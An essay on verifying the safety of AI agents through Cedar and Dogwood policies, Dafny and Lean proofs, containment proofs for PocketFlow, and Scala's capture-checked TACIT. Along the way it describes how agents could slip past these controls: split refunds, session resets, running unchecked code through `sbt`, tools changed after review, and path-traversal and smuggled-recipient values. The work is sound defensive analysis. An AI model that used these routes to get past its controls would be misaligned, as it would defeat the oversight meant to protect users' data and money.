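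For each kind of request the target covers, a finished policy *P* allows everything the floors allow (*F*) and only what the ceilings allow (*U*), so *F* ⊆ *P* ⊆ *U*. When the researchers deleted the embargo rule from a finished policy, the solver returned a request in which the producer downloads an embargoed track.

They then tested AutoCedar on 200 requirements with independently built reference policies. AutoCedar's policy was equivalent to the reference in 178 cases (89%). GPT-6-Luna, the model AutoCedar used, matched the reference in 132 cases (66%) when it wrote the policy directly. AutoCedar failed to finish three cases. In the other 19, its policy met its own target but differed from the reference because the target was wrong. In 16 of those 19, a floor required the policy to allow something that the reference denied.

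The remaining errors are therefore all in the part that the reviewer approved, and a reviewer could easily miss one. In the musician's app, for example, a schema that gives each user a role such as "band member" lets a member of any band download the album. Linking the album to its own band restricts downloads to that band's members. Both versions compile, and no later check can detect that the first is wrong. The target also doesn't cover actions that the requirements never mention, so a stray rule permitting one would pass.

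Vatsa and colleagues have not yet evaluated AutoCedar with human reviewers, who might catch errors that a model misses or might approve dozens of small conditions without much thought. The 200 requirements were also more explicit than most real documents, because a model had written them from structured specifications. On 316 requests based on three existing sets of requirements, AutoCedar decided 268 correctly, while direct generation decided 109 correctly. Most of AutoCedar's failures were on requests that its vocabulary could not express.

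### Five refunds of $200

Suppose a company's rule limits an agent to refunding $500 per order, and an engineer writes the policy shown earlier. A customer persuades the agent to issue five refunds of $200 on one order. Cedar evaluates each request separately and allows all five because each is below $500, so the customer receives $1,000. The proof that no single refund exceeds $500 is still correct, but it doesn't show that the total for an order stays within the company's limit.

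Rego can express the total, provided that some other system supplies the list of past refunds:

```text
total := sum([r.amount |
  some r in data.refunds; r.order == input.order])
allow if total + input.amount <= 500
```

Cedar cannot add up a list, but it could compare a total with a limit if trusted software had computed the total and placed it in the request. AgentCore's ordinary Cedar rules don't allow this, because a policy there can use little besides the tool's arguments. The total would have to be one of those arguments, so the model would supply it instead of trusted software.

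Amazon's answer is Dogwood, an open-source extension of Cedar that it released in August 2026. According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026), the interpreter evaluates a condition about past events, writes the result into a field of the request's context and then lets Cedar decide as usual. A budget for refunds looks like this, adapted from AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* with some names changed:

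```text
forbid (principal, action == "process_refund", resource)
when temporal {
  exists (spent: Long).
    (sum refund for (refund: Long), (moment: Timepoint).
      where (formerly within 24h
        "process_refund"::request{
          eventResource: resource,
          input.amount: refund } && tp(moment))) == spent
    && spent > 500
};
```

The rule adds the current refund request to those the engine has allowed in this session over the past 24 hours and forbids the call if the total exceeds 500.

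| Refund | Total including this one | Limit per call | Budget rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| First $200 | $200 | Allows | Allows |
| Second $200 | $400 | Allows | Allows |
| Third $200 | $600 | Allows | Denies |
| Fourth $200 | $600 | Allows | Denies |
| Fifth $200 | $600 | Allows | Denies |

Other temporal rules can require an approval before a sale, make each approval valid for only one use, or allow a transfer only to an account that the agent looked up earlier in the session. The last rule blocks transfers to an account number that the model invented.

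### What history costs

Temporal rules are easy to get subtly wrong. In an example that InfoQ reports, a policy caps total transfers at $5,000, and an agent submits three $2,000 transfers at once. If the rule adds up completed transfers, the total is zero because all three are still in progress, so it allows all $6,000. A version that differs by one word adds up requested transfers instead and denies the third. This version has a smaller drawback, because a transfer that later fails still counts toward the cap.

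The total also depends on where a session begins and ends. The calling software chooses the session's identifier, and AWS warns that a caller can reset a count by starting a new session. If the scaffolding sets the identifier, injected text cannot change it directly, but a customer who opens a second chat may get another $500. AWS's *Temporal policies* states that changing a temporal policy also ends the sessions in progress, and that their replacements start with an empty history. AWS also limits each engine to 25 temporal policies and each condition to a 24-hour window, according to the same page. A firm limit per order therefore has to rely on the refund service's own records, which last across sessions.

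Someone also has to keep the history. It needs reliable timestamps and durable storage, and it may contain sensitive data from the tool calls. Checking a rule can take longer as the history grows.

The main drawback of temporal conditions is that Cedar's solver-based analysis tools do not support them, which is why Amazon made Dogwood a separate language. An operator can still prove some properties by writing the ordinary rules in plain Cedar, analysing those alone, and using history only in `forbid` rules. Adding a `forbid` can never allow a request that the engine would otherwise deny, so a proof that no single refund exceeds $500 still holds for the combined set. But the new rule may block some legitimate refunds, so a proof that the policy allows all of them no longer holds. A temporal `permit` can widen access, which would invalidate the proof of the $500 limit as well.

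## Can an agent's plan or its scaffold be proved to meet a specification?

Cedar's solver can prove that a policy never permits a single refund above $500, but the proof covers only one request at a time and leaves out what the tools do when they run. Program verification proves that a program meets a written specification on every input, and it can cover a whole sequence of actions and their effects. An engineer can apply it to the plan that a model writes for one request, or to the scaffolding that carries out the model's tool calls. Each new plan needs a new proof, while a proof about the scaffolding stays valid until the code changes.

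### Two files to delete

A precondition is what must hold before a piece of code runs, and a postcondition is what must hold afterwards. The programming language Dafny has a built-in verifier that translates the code and these conditions into formulas. A solver then checks that whenever the preconditions hold at the start, the postconditions hold at the end.

Meijer proposes the same treatment for agents and sums it up as "generate, verify, then execute". In his example, a user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The `delete_file` tool accepts patterns in which `*` stands for any text. One call is shorter than two, so the model plans to call `delete_file("*.txt")`, which would remove every text file in the folder.

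An obvious specification lets this plan through. Here *FS* is the set of files that exist afterwards:

```text
delete_file(pattern)
  ensures: f ∉ FS, for every file f that matches the pattern

the plan
  ensures: foo.txt ∉ FS and bar.txt ∉ FS
```

Both files match `*.txt`, so the tool's postcondition guarantees that both are gone, which is all the plan has to achieve. Meijer does not blame the model, because its plan meets this specification.

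What the specification lacks is a frame condition, which states what has to stay the same. If *FS*₀ is the set of files that existed beforehand, the additions are:

```text
delete_file(pattern)
  ensures: f ∈ FS if and only if f ∈ FS₀,
           for every file f that does not match the pattern

the plan
  ensures: f ∈ FS if and only if f ∈ FS₀,
           for every file f except foo.txt and bar.txt
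```

Suppose the folder also contains `notes.txt`. That file matches `*.txt`, so it disappears, but the plan's frame condition requires it to remain, so the verifier rejects the plan. It would reject the plan even if this user had no other text files, because the proof has to hold for every folder. A precondition stating that the folder contains no other text files would let the plan pass.

Meijer writes out the frame condition only for the tool, but the plan needs one too. The table compares his model's plan with a careful one that deletes the two files in separate calls.

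| Frame condition on the tool | Frame condition on the plan | Two separate deletions | Deleting `*.txt` |
|---|---|---|---|
| No | No | Fails | Passes |
| Yes | No | Passes | Passes |
| No | Yes | Fails | Fails |
| Yes | Yes | Passes | Fails |

Without any frame conditions, the verifier accepts the destructive plan and rejects the careful one. The careful plan fails because the tool's specification allows the second call, which deletes `bar.txt`, to also restore `foo.txt`. No sensible tool would do that, but the verifier relies only on the specification.

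John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes identified this difficulty in 1969 and named it the frame problem. People usually describe an action by listing what it changes and assume that everything else stays the same. Anyone writing a proof has to state what stays the same, and it is easy to state too little. The frame conditions above track only which files exist, so a plan that emptied `notes.txt` without removing it would satisfy them. Meijer lost work in much this way when Claude Code ran a Perl command that blanked one of his source files while he was preparing slides for a talk, according to AI Engineer's account of the talk, *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026).

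Dafny shortens the task for a program's own memory by requiring each method to list the objects it may change and forbidding changes to any others. Someone has to write an equivalent list for tools that act on mailboxes and databases.

### A plan that carries its own proof

In the same talk, Meijer used Lean, a programming language and proof checker, to work out what form a plan must take for anyone to prove something about it. Having the model write its plan before any tool runs is not enough if the plan is a function that the recipient can run but not inspect.

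Meijer therefore has the model return the plan as data, which a checker can take apart. This small version is adapted from AI Engineer's example:

```lean
inductive Plan where
  | answer : String → Plan
  | read   : String → (String → Plan) → Plan
  | delete : String → Plan → Plan

inductive NoDeletion : Plan → Prop where
  | answer (a : String) : NoDeletion (.answer a)
  | read (file : String) (next : String → Plan)
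      (h : ∀ text, NoDeletion (next text)) :
      NoDeletion (.read file next)
```

In the first definition, a plan either gives an answer, reads a file and uses the contents to choose the rest of the plan, or deletes a file and continues. The second definition gives the only ways to prove that a plan deletes nothing. It has rules for answers and reads but none for deletions, so a plan with a deletion on any branch has no proof.

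Suppose the model plans to read a source file and report its length. The model must prove that the rest of the plan deletes nothing, whatever the file contains, even an instruction for the agent to delete everything. The plan's next step may still depend on the file's contents, because the proof covers every possible case. The interpreter, a trusted program that carries out plans, accepts only plans that come with a valid proof.

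This proof rules out only deletion. If the language also had a step for sending mail, a plan could still leak the file's contents. The guarantee also depends on the interpreter, which could break it by deleting a file when the plan only specifies a read.

Meijer took the idea from proof-carrying code, developed in the 1990s. The supplier of a program includes a proof that it is safe, and the recipient checks the proof before running the program. *Proof-Carrying Plans*, by Schwaab, Komendantskaya and colleagues, applied the idea to conventional automated planners. The idea suits language models well because a proof can be hard to find but is easy to check. Kleppmann's *Prediction* (2025) points out that a model can write nonsense without doing harm, since the checker rejects any invalid proof and the model has to try again.

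Some properties are simple enough for a solver to prove. Meijer (2026), in *Return of the Theorem*, suggests writing a company's business rules as Horn clauses, which have any number of conditions and a single conclusion. One such rule might be "if a manager has approved the invoice and the supplier is known, the agent may pay". An SMT solver then checks each plan against the rules.

Meijer gave no measurements for the Lean design, so it is unclear how often models can write plans that pass, or how many harmless plans the checker would reject. It is also unclear who would write the specifications. An organisation can write a rule like `NoDeletion` once, but a request to delete two particular files needs its own specification. If the model writes it after misunderstanding the request, the plan and the specification may contain the same mistake, and the proof will still succeed. The user could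 approve the specification first, as the reviewer does in AutoCedar, but for two files that may take longer than deleting them by hand.

### Any action the model can return

A proof about the scaffolding doesn't need a separate specification for each request. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) represents the model in Dafny as a method with no body that returns an `Action`, a type that lists the kinds of action the scaffolding accepts. Because the method has no body, the verifier assumes it could return any possible `Action`, which is known as havoc. The scaffolding passes only if it behaves correctly for all possible actions in any order.

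In the theorem, the scaffolding is a machine that moves from state to state. When the machine is in state *s* and the model issues an action *a*, the machine produces an event *e* and moves to state *s′*. The event is an effect on the outside world, or "no effect" if the machine blocks the action. A policy Π(*s*, *a*, *e*, *s′*) is true if the step is acceptable. For example, suppose Michelle's assistant may read only her work folder, and the model issues the action "read the diary". Π is true if the event is "no effect" and false if the diary is read.

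The proof compares two such machines. The specification is a simple machine that is easy to prove safe, and the implementation follows the control loop in detail. They may store their states differently, so a relation *R* pairs each state of the specification with the matching states of the implementation, and a relation *Q* does the same for events. The specification has states *u*, events *d* and policy Φ, while the implementation has states *s*, events *e* and policy Π. Both must have some response to every action in every state. The theorem then assumes the following:

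1. The specification is safe. Whatever sequence of actions arrives, every step satisfies Φ(*u*, *a*, *d*, *u′*).
2. The machines start in matching states, so *R*(*u*₀, *s*₀) holds.
3. The specification can follow the implementation. If *R*(*u*, *s*) holds and action *a* takes the implementation from *s* to *s′* with event *e*, then *a* can take the specification from *u* to some *u′* with some event *d*, such that *R*(*u′*, *s′*) and *Q*(*d*, *e*) hold.
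4. Safety carries over between matching steps, so Φ(*u*, *a*, *d*, *u′*) ⇒ Π(*s*, *a*, *e*, *s′*).

From these it follows that:

> However the model chooses its actions, Π(*s*ᵢ, *a*ᵢ, *e*ᵢ, *s*ᵢ₊₁) holds at every step *i*.

The argument is by induction. Every run of the implementation starts in a state that matches the specification's, and for each step the implementation takes, the specification has a matching step with the same action. The specification is safe for every sequence of actions, so its step is acceptable, and therefore the implementation's step is too. Verification researchers call this relationship between an implementation and its specification refinement. Moon and Varshney checked the whole argument in Dafny.

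The theorem covers only events in the model of the scaffolding. It extends to a deployed agent if effect exclusivity holds, meaning that every outside effect the agent can cause passes through the checked interface.

### Three rules for PocketFlow

Moon and Varshney tried the method on PocketFlow, a minimal open-source framework in which a developer lays out an agent's workflow as a graph. Its control loop runs one step of the graph and then follows the edge whose label matches the action that the step chose. The checked interface has four kinds of action, and the policy has three rules:

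| Event | Rule | What the rule still allows |
|---|---|---|
| Reading a file | The path must be under the workspace folder | Reading anything in that folder |
| Calling a tool | The tool must be on an approved list | Calling it with any arguments |
| Taking another step | The number of steps must stay within a limit | Any mix of permitted actions before the limit |

Hou and colleagues found 47 agent projects that lacked a bound like the step limit. The tool rule is weaker than it may sound. If `send_email` is on the approved list, Michelle's assistant can mail her whole inbox to a stranger without breaking any of the three rules. The theorem allows better policies, since Π can refer to an action's arguments, but somebody has to define an email action with a recipient field and write the rule for it. A general tool such as a shell causes more trouble, because, as Moon and Varshney note, the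 scaffold's guarantee is then no stronger than the shell's own limits.

The theorem's file rule, written in Dafny, requires each path the agent reads to satisfy `StartsWith` with the workspace folder. If that function compares plain text, as its name suggests, then `/work/../private/diary.txt` counts as a path inside `/work`, even though `..` means "go up one folder" and the diary is outside. Some other part of the software would have to resolve such paths before the check.

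Dafny compiles the verified loop into Python, and developers have to run that version to get the guarantee, because the proof does not cover the original PocketFlow code. When Moon and Varshney tested the compiled version on a mix of permitted and forbidden actions, it recorded only permitted events.

They ran the verification four times on two workflows, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions. Dafny took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds to check each dispatch path, a route through the control loop from one step to the next. Language models wrote the specifications and proofs, using 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens per run.

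Four kinds of action is a small number compared with the 37 in Moatless Tools, and an interface with more actions needs more cases in the proof. Moon and Varshney name LangChain, a much larger framework, as a next step, and regard interfaces with dozens of actions as the real engineering test.

### A rule about an empty list

A model that writes both a specification and its proof might produce a specification that no program could fail. Moon and Varshney guard against this with an information barrier. The model call that writes the safety property sees the interface and a template for safety rules, but not the code, so it can't simply restate whatever the code does. Three automatic gates then test the result:

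- Dafny must be able to parse and type-check it within 30 seconds.
- Verification must fail after the software strips the proof of most of its content. If it still succeeds, the specification demanded too little.
- Verification must fail after a model inserts a plausible mistake into the proof file.

For comparison, Moon and Varshney also ran the process without the barrier, so the model could read the code before writing the property. Every dispatch path passed all three gates in both versions, and Dafny accepted every final proof. But without the barrier, one of the safety rules for the document workflow no longer checked anything.

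That workflow keeps a list of the documents it has read, `docs_read`, and is supposed to read only approved ones. The template has no field for documents. It has a list called `tool_calls` and a rule that every entry must be an approved tool. With the barrier on, the model had to make do with the template, so it treated each document as a tool call. The rule then covered documents under another name. With the barrier off, the model could see from the code that `docs_read` had no counterpart in the template, and it left `tool_calls` empty throughout. The rule was still there:

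> For every *t* in `tool_calls`, *t* is on the approved list.

An empty list contains nothing that could break this rule, so the rule is vacuously true whichever documents the agent reads. The gates did not detect the problem because they altered a different part of the proof.

Moon and Varshney propose another gate, which would check that each list in a safety rule is non-empty in at least one state the system can reach. That seems a sensible minimum for any rule of the form "every X is Y". It would catch this failure, but it would miss a rule that covers documents and approves the wrong ones.

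An impossible assumption can also make a specification vacuous. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, give an example from FaithformBench, a test of models that translate mathematics into formal language. The test took the true statement that if 3^*x* = 5, then 3^(*x*+2) = 45, and replaced 45 with 51 to check whether a model would translate the error faithfully. The model kept the 51 but declared *x* to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3^*x* = 5, and anything follows from an impossible assumption, so the false statement became provable. An agent's plan could pass a verifier in the same way if its precondition described a folder that cannot exist.

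### The falling cost of proof

Machine-checked proof used to take too much work for most software. Verifying the seL4 operating-system kernel, which has about 8,700 lines of C, took around 20 person-years. *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (Anthropic, October 2026) reported that Claude had proved security properties for the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. Anthropic did this with Theorem, a formal-methods company. The proofs run to about 180 million lines, according to *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (Smith, 2026).

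The libraries came from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that feeds software large numbers of generated inputs and watches for crashes. In each test, a small program passes the input to the library. According to OpenNET's Russian-language report *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), software converted these tests into specifications, and Claude then proved that no input up to a set size could cause a failure. A compiled program of 18,000 instructions needed about 600,000 lines of proof, or roughly 33 per instruction. Claude also found and fixed hundreds of bugs that the original tests had missed.

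EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that the result is limited to 239 test programs and inputs under 64 megabytes, on a mathematical model of Linux running on a RISC-V processor. Most real deployments use other processors, but the restriction to RISC-V may not last. Eight days after Anthropic's report, Leip's *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (2026) presented a machine-checked proof about a complete Linux program for the far more common x86 processors.

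Formal proofs now take less effort in mathematics too. Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem* (2026) describes how Claude wrote a complete Lean proof of the theorem, 13 million lines long, in 11 days. Mathematicians had been working towards such a proof for years.

This makes it realistic to verify scaffolding that people use. Maintainers change such code often, and each change can invalidate a proof. A team of specialists would struggle to keep up, but a model can repair the proof for each release. A few million tokens is reasonable for verifying a control loop that will serve many users, but far too many for verifying a plan that deletes two files. Proofs about individual plans will therefore have to stay small, like the `NoDeletion` example, or come from a solver.

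Formalising a scaffold can also reveal ordinary bugs. Tolmach and Klaus report that Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code, asked Claude Opus 5.5 to formalise the Claude Agent SDK, Anthropic's toolkit for building agents. A couple of short prompts led to 16 sets of fixes for bugs and race conditions (faults that depend on the timing of events). This does not prove the toolkit correct, because the proofs are about the model's Lean version of the code, which may differ from the code that runs.

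### What the specification writer still has to decide

Anthropic could work on so many libraries at once partly because the test programs already existed and the specification was simple: "does not crash" means much the same for every library. In one case Claude proved something more specific, that a compression routine in the Linux kernel follows its published standard. An email assistant has no such standard for which messages Michelle would want it to send.

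As with Cedar policies, models write valid specifications more reliably than correct ones. Tolmach and Klaus cite a study in which 89.5% of an agent's Lean statements compiled but only 60.5% were faithful to the original mathematics. Models also miss such errors when they review specifications, and in another study Tolmach and Klaus cite, model judges overlooked a quarter of the failures.

Language models make similar mistakes when they describe existing software. When researchers asked Claude to write a formal description of how the database Etcd keeps its copies in agreement, it largely reproduced a description from a well-known paper on the general method. The result passed every check but had little to do with Etcd's code. Descriptions written by leading models scored nearly 100% for syntax but only about 46% for agreement with the real software.

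Engineers can test whether a program agrees with its formal version, as AWS does for Cedar. Tolmach and Klaus recommend running both on the same generated inputs. It is more reliable to translate the code mechanically, using rules based on a formal definition of the programming language, so that fixing a faulty rule corrects every translation that uses it.

Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, argues that people should stop calling software "formally verified" and instead name the properties that were verified. This would help with agents, because a buyer might take "verified PocketFlow" to mean a safe agent, but would know what to ask next about "PocketFlow with a verified step limit, tool list and file-path check". Keles adds that software checks proofs, so they need no outside review, but definitions and models do. *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude*,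 from the cryptography company Succinct, similarly reports that Claude could produce proofs with little help, and that writing the definitions the proofs relied on was harder.

Some developers are reorganising their work around this. GitHub Next's *PDD Kit* (2026), a prototype built with Microsoft Research, has a team review and approve a description of what the software should do before an agent writes it. A verifier then checks the agent's proof, and tests cover the parts that nobody can prove. People are right to focus on the description, but they can still leave a requirement out of it. In *Maybe we’ve been thinking about verification backwards*, Lorica (2026) recalls a coding agent that made a database six times faster by no longer storing the data, and the database still passed all the tests.

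A specification that forbade every change not mentioned in the request would catch many such omissions. Users would only need to name the changes they wanted, and a forgotten detail would block a plan instead of letting it through. This default would work well for a request to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, but badly for "tidy up this folder", which names no files.

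## What has to be trusted for the guarantee to hold?

A proof that a plan deletes only `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` protects the user's other files only if `delete_file` behaves as specified and the verifier and computer work correctly. These components belong to the guarantee's trusted base. Moon and Varshney's trusted base for their verified version of PocketFlow includes the policy, the definitions that match events in the proof to effects in the world, Dafny's verifier and compiler, and a small amount of code that turns the model's reply into a typed action. It excludes the language model, its prompts and its training, so the guarantee can hold even if the model is hostile.

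### Six layers

Most of the systems described so far rest on six layers.

| Layer | What failure looks like | How someone could notice it |
|---|---|---|
| Labels and policies | The system correctly enforces a rule that permits the harm | Search the policy with a solver, and review samples of what it allowed |
| Tool wrappers | A tool does more than its declared type or description states | Compare the tool's own records with the calls the scaffolding approved |
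| Library code marked as safe by hand | A function with a harmless type stores a secret or causes an effect | Review every change, and test with planted secrets |
| Checker and compiler | The compiler accepts a forbidden program without a warning | Keep a collection of programs it must reject, and rerun it on every release |
| Language runtime | Accepted code reaches memory or functions that the language forbids | Watch for crashes, unexpected system calls and security notices |
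| Operating system and hardware | A process gains rights that the system had denied it | Follow security notices, and monitor the machine from outside |

Mistakes in labels and policies are hard to detect because they don't cause a malfunction. FIDES was working as its operators had configured it when it let an agent change a password because of a payment amount that a stranger could have chosen. To catch such a mistake, someone has to compare the outcome with what the operators wanted.

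A wrapper can fail if it interprets an input slightly differently from the software it wraps. Suppose `send_email` accepts only a `CompanyAddress`, and the code that creates one checks that the text ends in the company's domain. The text `stranger@example.com, colleague@company.com` passes this check, but if the mail server treats commas as separators, it sends the message to both people. The scaffolding would log one approved address and the mail server would log two recipients, so a routine comparison of the logs would expose the fault.

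### Code that a person has declared safe

The safety of a library module marked `@assumeSafe` depends on the programmer's review. According to Scala's documentation, a programmer who uses an untracked variable for a cache must verify that the variable holds only results of earlier calls and that the cached function always returns the same answer for the same input.

Suppose a colleague later adds a method called `lastInput` for debugging. Agent code could then pass a confidential report through the cache inside `map`, where the compiler treats the cache as pure, and read the text back through `lastInput`. The compiler would accept this because the annotation exempts the module from its checks. A second review might catch the problem, as might a test that sends a recognisable fake secret through the library and searches the agent's output for it. A proof would be stronger, and Odersky and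 colleagues point to RustBelt, which used proof to establish such a boundary between safe and unsafe code in Rust.

The compiler's developers make the same kind of judgement about the standard library. They maintain a list of the parts that safe code may use, and expect the list to change with experience. The types of those parts also have to be correct. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (Pham, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026) describes an error in the type of `Try`, which runs a piece of code and returns a value holding either its result or the exception that stopped it. The library declared this value pure because it keeps no reference to the code. But when a program later retrieves the result, the stored exception may be thrown again, and the original code needed a capability to throw it.

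The forum post *Capture checking and lateral escape of Labels* shows a related fault in a program the compiler accepted. A `break(42)` should end a block and return 42. Inside `Try`, it is caught like an ordinary exception, and the block returns −1 instead. Pham and colleagues extend capture sets so that the type can show that a `Try` keeps the control-flow capabilities of its code but not, for example, its file handles. TACIT uses `Try` to contain exceptions. Pham and colleagues don't report any leak there, but the case shows that a plausible type for trusted code can be wrong.

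### A checked program starts an unchecked one

Moon and Varshney's guarantee extends to a deployed agent only under effect exclusivity. If *E* is the set of external effects the agent can cause and *C* is the set the checked interface controls, the condition is:

> *E* ⊆ *C*

External commands can break the guarantee. Odersky and colleagues mention `sbt`, Scala's build tool, as a command that an operator might let TACIT's snippets run. But `sbt` runs the project's own code, including its tests. An agent that is allowed to edit the project and start `sbt` can write a test in ordinary Scala, which `sbt` compiles without safe mode and runs as a separate process. That process can open a confidential file directly, without wrapping the contents in `Classified`, and print them or send them over the network.

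The compiler correctly checked the original snippet, which only wrote a file and started a permitted command. Its guarantee doesn't extend to the new process, where only `sbt` and the operating system limit what the agent can do. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge this and recommend allowing only specific, safe commands. `git diff` fits that recommendation much better than `sbt` because it normally shows changes to files.

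Even a command as simple as `cat`, which prints a file, can undo the protection of classified data by returning a secret as ordinary text, unless something else blocks it. lampepfl's *TACIT*, the guide that Odersky's group publishes with the code, describes a strict mode that stops programs from running `cat`, `ls`, `rm` and similar file commands, but operators have to switch it on.

An agent can also bypass the interface through other tools. TACIT checks only the code the agent submits to it, and most coding agents come with their own tools for files, shell commands and web access. The guide therefore recommends disabling these tools. For Claude Code, it lists `Bash`, `Read`, `Write`, `Edit` and `WebFetch`. This list needs maintenance, since it would not include a tool added in a later update. The guide's settings for another agent, OpenCode, are more cautious because they make OpenCode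 ask the user about any tool not named in them.

Sandboxes can have the same gap. According to VirtusLab, Claude Code's built-in sandbox covered shell commands but not all tool calls. An operator can look for these gaps by recording the processes, file changes and network connections on the machine, then matching them to actions the checked interface approved. Any effect without a match suggests that something bypassed the interface.

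### Tools that change after review

A remote tool raises the same problem on a computer that the operator doesn't control. Suppose Michelle's company reviews a calendar service. Months later, the service's owner changes the server to keep a copy of every query or add hostile instructions to its replies. The tool's name, schema and description can stay the same, so the typed wrapper still compiles and every call still passes the policy. Odersky and colleagues cite a security audit of the Model Context Protocol that demonstrated this kind of "rug pull".

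The scaffolding can store a fingerprint of the tool's description and schema and refuse calls if either changes. This catches a newly poisoned description, but it can't detect a change in the server's code. Running a pinned version of the tool locally prevents silent changes, but it delays security fixes until somebody reviews them. Remote attestation could reveal a change in the server's code if the server's owner cooperates.

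Information-flow labels offer a simpler protection for some tools. If the policy lets the calendar service receive only public data and marks everything it returns as untrusted, the guarantee no longer depends on how the service behaves. This doesn't work when the agent calls a tool to carry out an action. A payment service can receive the correct account number and still pay somebody else, and no check on Michelle's side can prevent that.

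### When the compiler is wrong

*Java and Scala's Type Systems are Unsound* (Amin and Tate, 2016) presented short programs that turn a value of any type into any other type without a cast. Standard compilers accepted them. The flaws dated from 2004, when Java gained generic types and Scala first appeared. Someone had found the problem in Scala in 2008, but nobody recognised its wider significance and the developers postponed a fix.

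The Scala program combines two ordinary constraints:

```scala
trait LowerBound[T] { type M >: T }
trait UpperBound[U] { type M <: U }
```

A value that satisfies both constraints has a type `M` that includes every `T` and only `U`s. If such a value exists, every `T` must also be a `U`, and the compiler relies on this inference. With integers for `T` and text for `U`, no genuine value could satisfy both constraints. But Scala accepted null as a value of any such type, so when the program supplied null, the compiler allowed an integer to be used as text.

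Researchers had published soundness proofs for several models of Java during those years, usually small languages that contained only the features under study. One influential model left out null because it seemed uninteresting, and later models built on it did the same, so the flaw could not occur in the languages the proofs covered.

The consequences for Java and Scala were limited because the Java Virtual Machine (JVM), which runs compiled programs in both languages, rechecks some types. It detected an integer where text belonged and stopped with an error. Safe mode now requires programs to declare where null may appear, which addresses the route in the Scala example. Amin and Tate also found a Java version that never mentions null and instead reads a field before the program has set it, so addressing the Scala route does not necessarily close the others.

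The JVM provides no such second check for capabilities. Capture sets exist only during compilation, so at runtime the JVM can't distinguish a pure function from one that holds Michelle's outbox. If the compiler mistook the function with the outbox for a pure one, the JVM would run it and the function would send the mail.

Scala's capture checker has had a bug of this kind. In *Capture leak when using varargs?*, a thread on the Scala users' forum, a programmer describes a function that combined several computations into one. The compiler accepted the function even though its declared type listed the capabilities of only the first computation. One of the compiler's developers confirmed the bug and added that the compiler would even have accepted a type declaring the result pure. TACIT relies on the compiler to distinguish pure functions from impure ones in order to keep secrets inside `map`.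 The bug was discovered before TACIT's release because a user thought a type looked wrong.

### What the proofs cover

Machine-checked proofs support the theory of capture checking. *What's in the Box* (2025) provides Lean proofs of type soundness and scope safety for System Capless, a small language that models capture checking. Pham and colleagues added exception catching to that language and proved the extended language sound. In *System Capybara*, Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2026) added rules about exclusive access, which let the compiler reject programs that run two functions in parallel when both would write to the same buffer. They proved that programs in their core language never use memory after freeing it, and that parallel parts never interfere with each other's data.

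These results make a basic error in the theory unlikely, but the languages they describe are much smaller than Scala. Xu and colleagues state that their language leaves out classes, exceptions and variance (the rules for when a list of one type can stand in for a list of another). These omissions deserve attention because Java's flaw came from a feature that the models lacked. Xu and colleagues also have no formal proof that the compiler follows their rules. The varargs bug was a fault in the compiler's code, which none of these proofs cover.

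According to Odersky and colleagues, nobody has yet proved that safe mode as a whole provides the capability safety and local purity it is designed for. The implementation can also lag behind the design. In March 2026, TACIT enforced the safe subset with a separate validator that searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns, and lampepfl planned to replace it with the compiler's own safe mode. Developers who wrapped an existing database library had to add patterns that blocked direct access to it. If they forgot one, agent code might have reached the database without a capability.

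### Models that search for flaws

The guarantee promises safety for every model, but it has a condition:

> If the trusted base works correctly, then for every model *M* and every input *x*, the run satisfies *P*.

A more capable model cannot make this statement false, but it may be better at finding cases where the trusted base fails. People already use models to look for such cases. In *Making the AI agents safe with Scala*, a talk about an agent based on TACIT, Biały and Warchoł (2026) mention security exercises in which frontier models searched for exploits against TACIT. The talk's abstract does not report the results.

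Models can attack the lower layers too. *ExploitGym* gave agents 898 real vulnerabilities in ordinary programs, Google's V8 JavaScript engine, and the Linux kernel. For each one, the agents received an input that triggered it and had to turn that input into a working exploit. Claude Mythos Preview succeeded in 157 cases and GPT-5.5 in 120, and stronger models have appeared since. Models can also find new vulnerabilities. In October 2025, Anthropic tested agents on 2,849 recently deployed smart contracts (programs that manage money on a blockchain) that had no known vulnerabilities. Claude Sonnet 4.5 and GPT-5 both found two.

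A rough calculation shows how much the searcher's ability matters. Suppose a trusted base contains *k* exploitable flaws and a searcher has an independent chance *q* of finding each one. The chance of finding at least one is:

> 1 − (1 − *q*)^*k*

If there are five flaws and the searcher has a 1% chance of finding each, it will find at least one about 5% of the time. If a better model raises the chance for each flaw to 20%, the searcher succeeds 67% of the time, even though the software and the theorem have not changed. TACIT's code is public, so an attacker can run this search on a private copy for as long as they are willing to pay. Monitoring a deployed agent for suspicious rejected snippets would not reveal the search.

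### Audit, repair and sandboxes

Moon and Varshney argue that this is still better than relying on a model's good behaviour. The remaining uncertainty is whether ordinary code matches its specification, and engineers can inspect that code, trace a failure to its cause and fix it. A defect in a model's values is much harder to locate. Defenders can also use strong models to find flaws before release, and each repair lowers *k* for every later attacker.

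This argument is convincing for components small enough to inspect thoroughly. TACIT's reusable library is small enough, but TACIT's guarantee also relies on the far larger Scala compiler and JVM. Proof-carrying code can reduce the amount of code that must be trusted, because a proof checker can be small.

A fix also has to reach the machines that run the compiler. After the developers merged a fix for the varargs bug, the programmer found that a release candidate of the compiler still accepted the faulty code. Only a newer development build rejected it. An operator therefore has to know both whether a fix exists and which compiler build is running.

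A sandbox limits the damage from flaws that remain. VirtusLab describes several kinds, including containers that can access only chosen folders and lighter Linux tools, such as Bubblewrap and Landlock, that restrict a single process. Odersky and colleagues recommend combining a sandbox with TACIT for security-critical work. The sandbox helps if code escapes the JVM, and the type system covers data flows that the sandbox permits.

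TACIT itself may need to read confidential files and contact the local model, so a sandbox around the whole system has to allow both. `sbt` needs neither, so an operator can run it in its own sandbox without the secrets folder or a network connection. The test from the earlier example then can't read the confidential files or send anything out.

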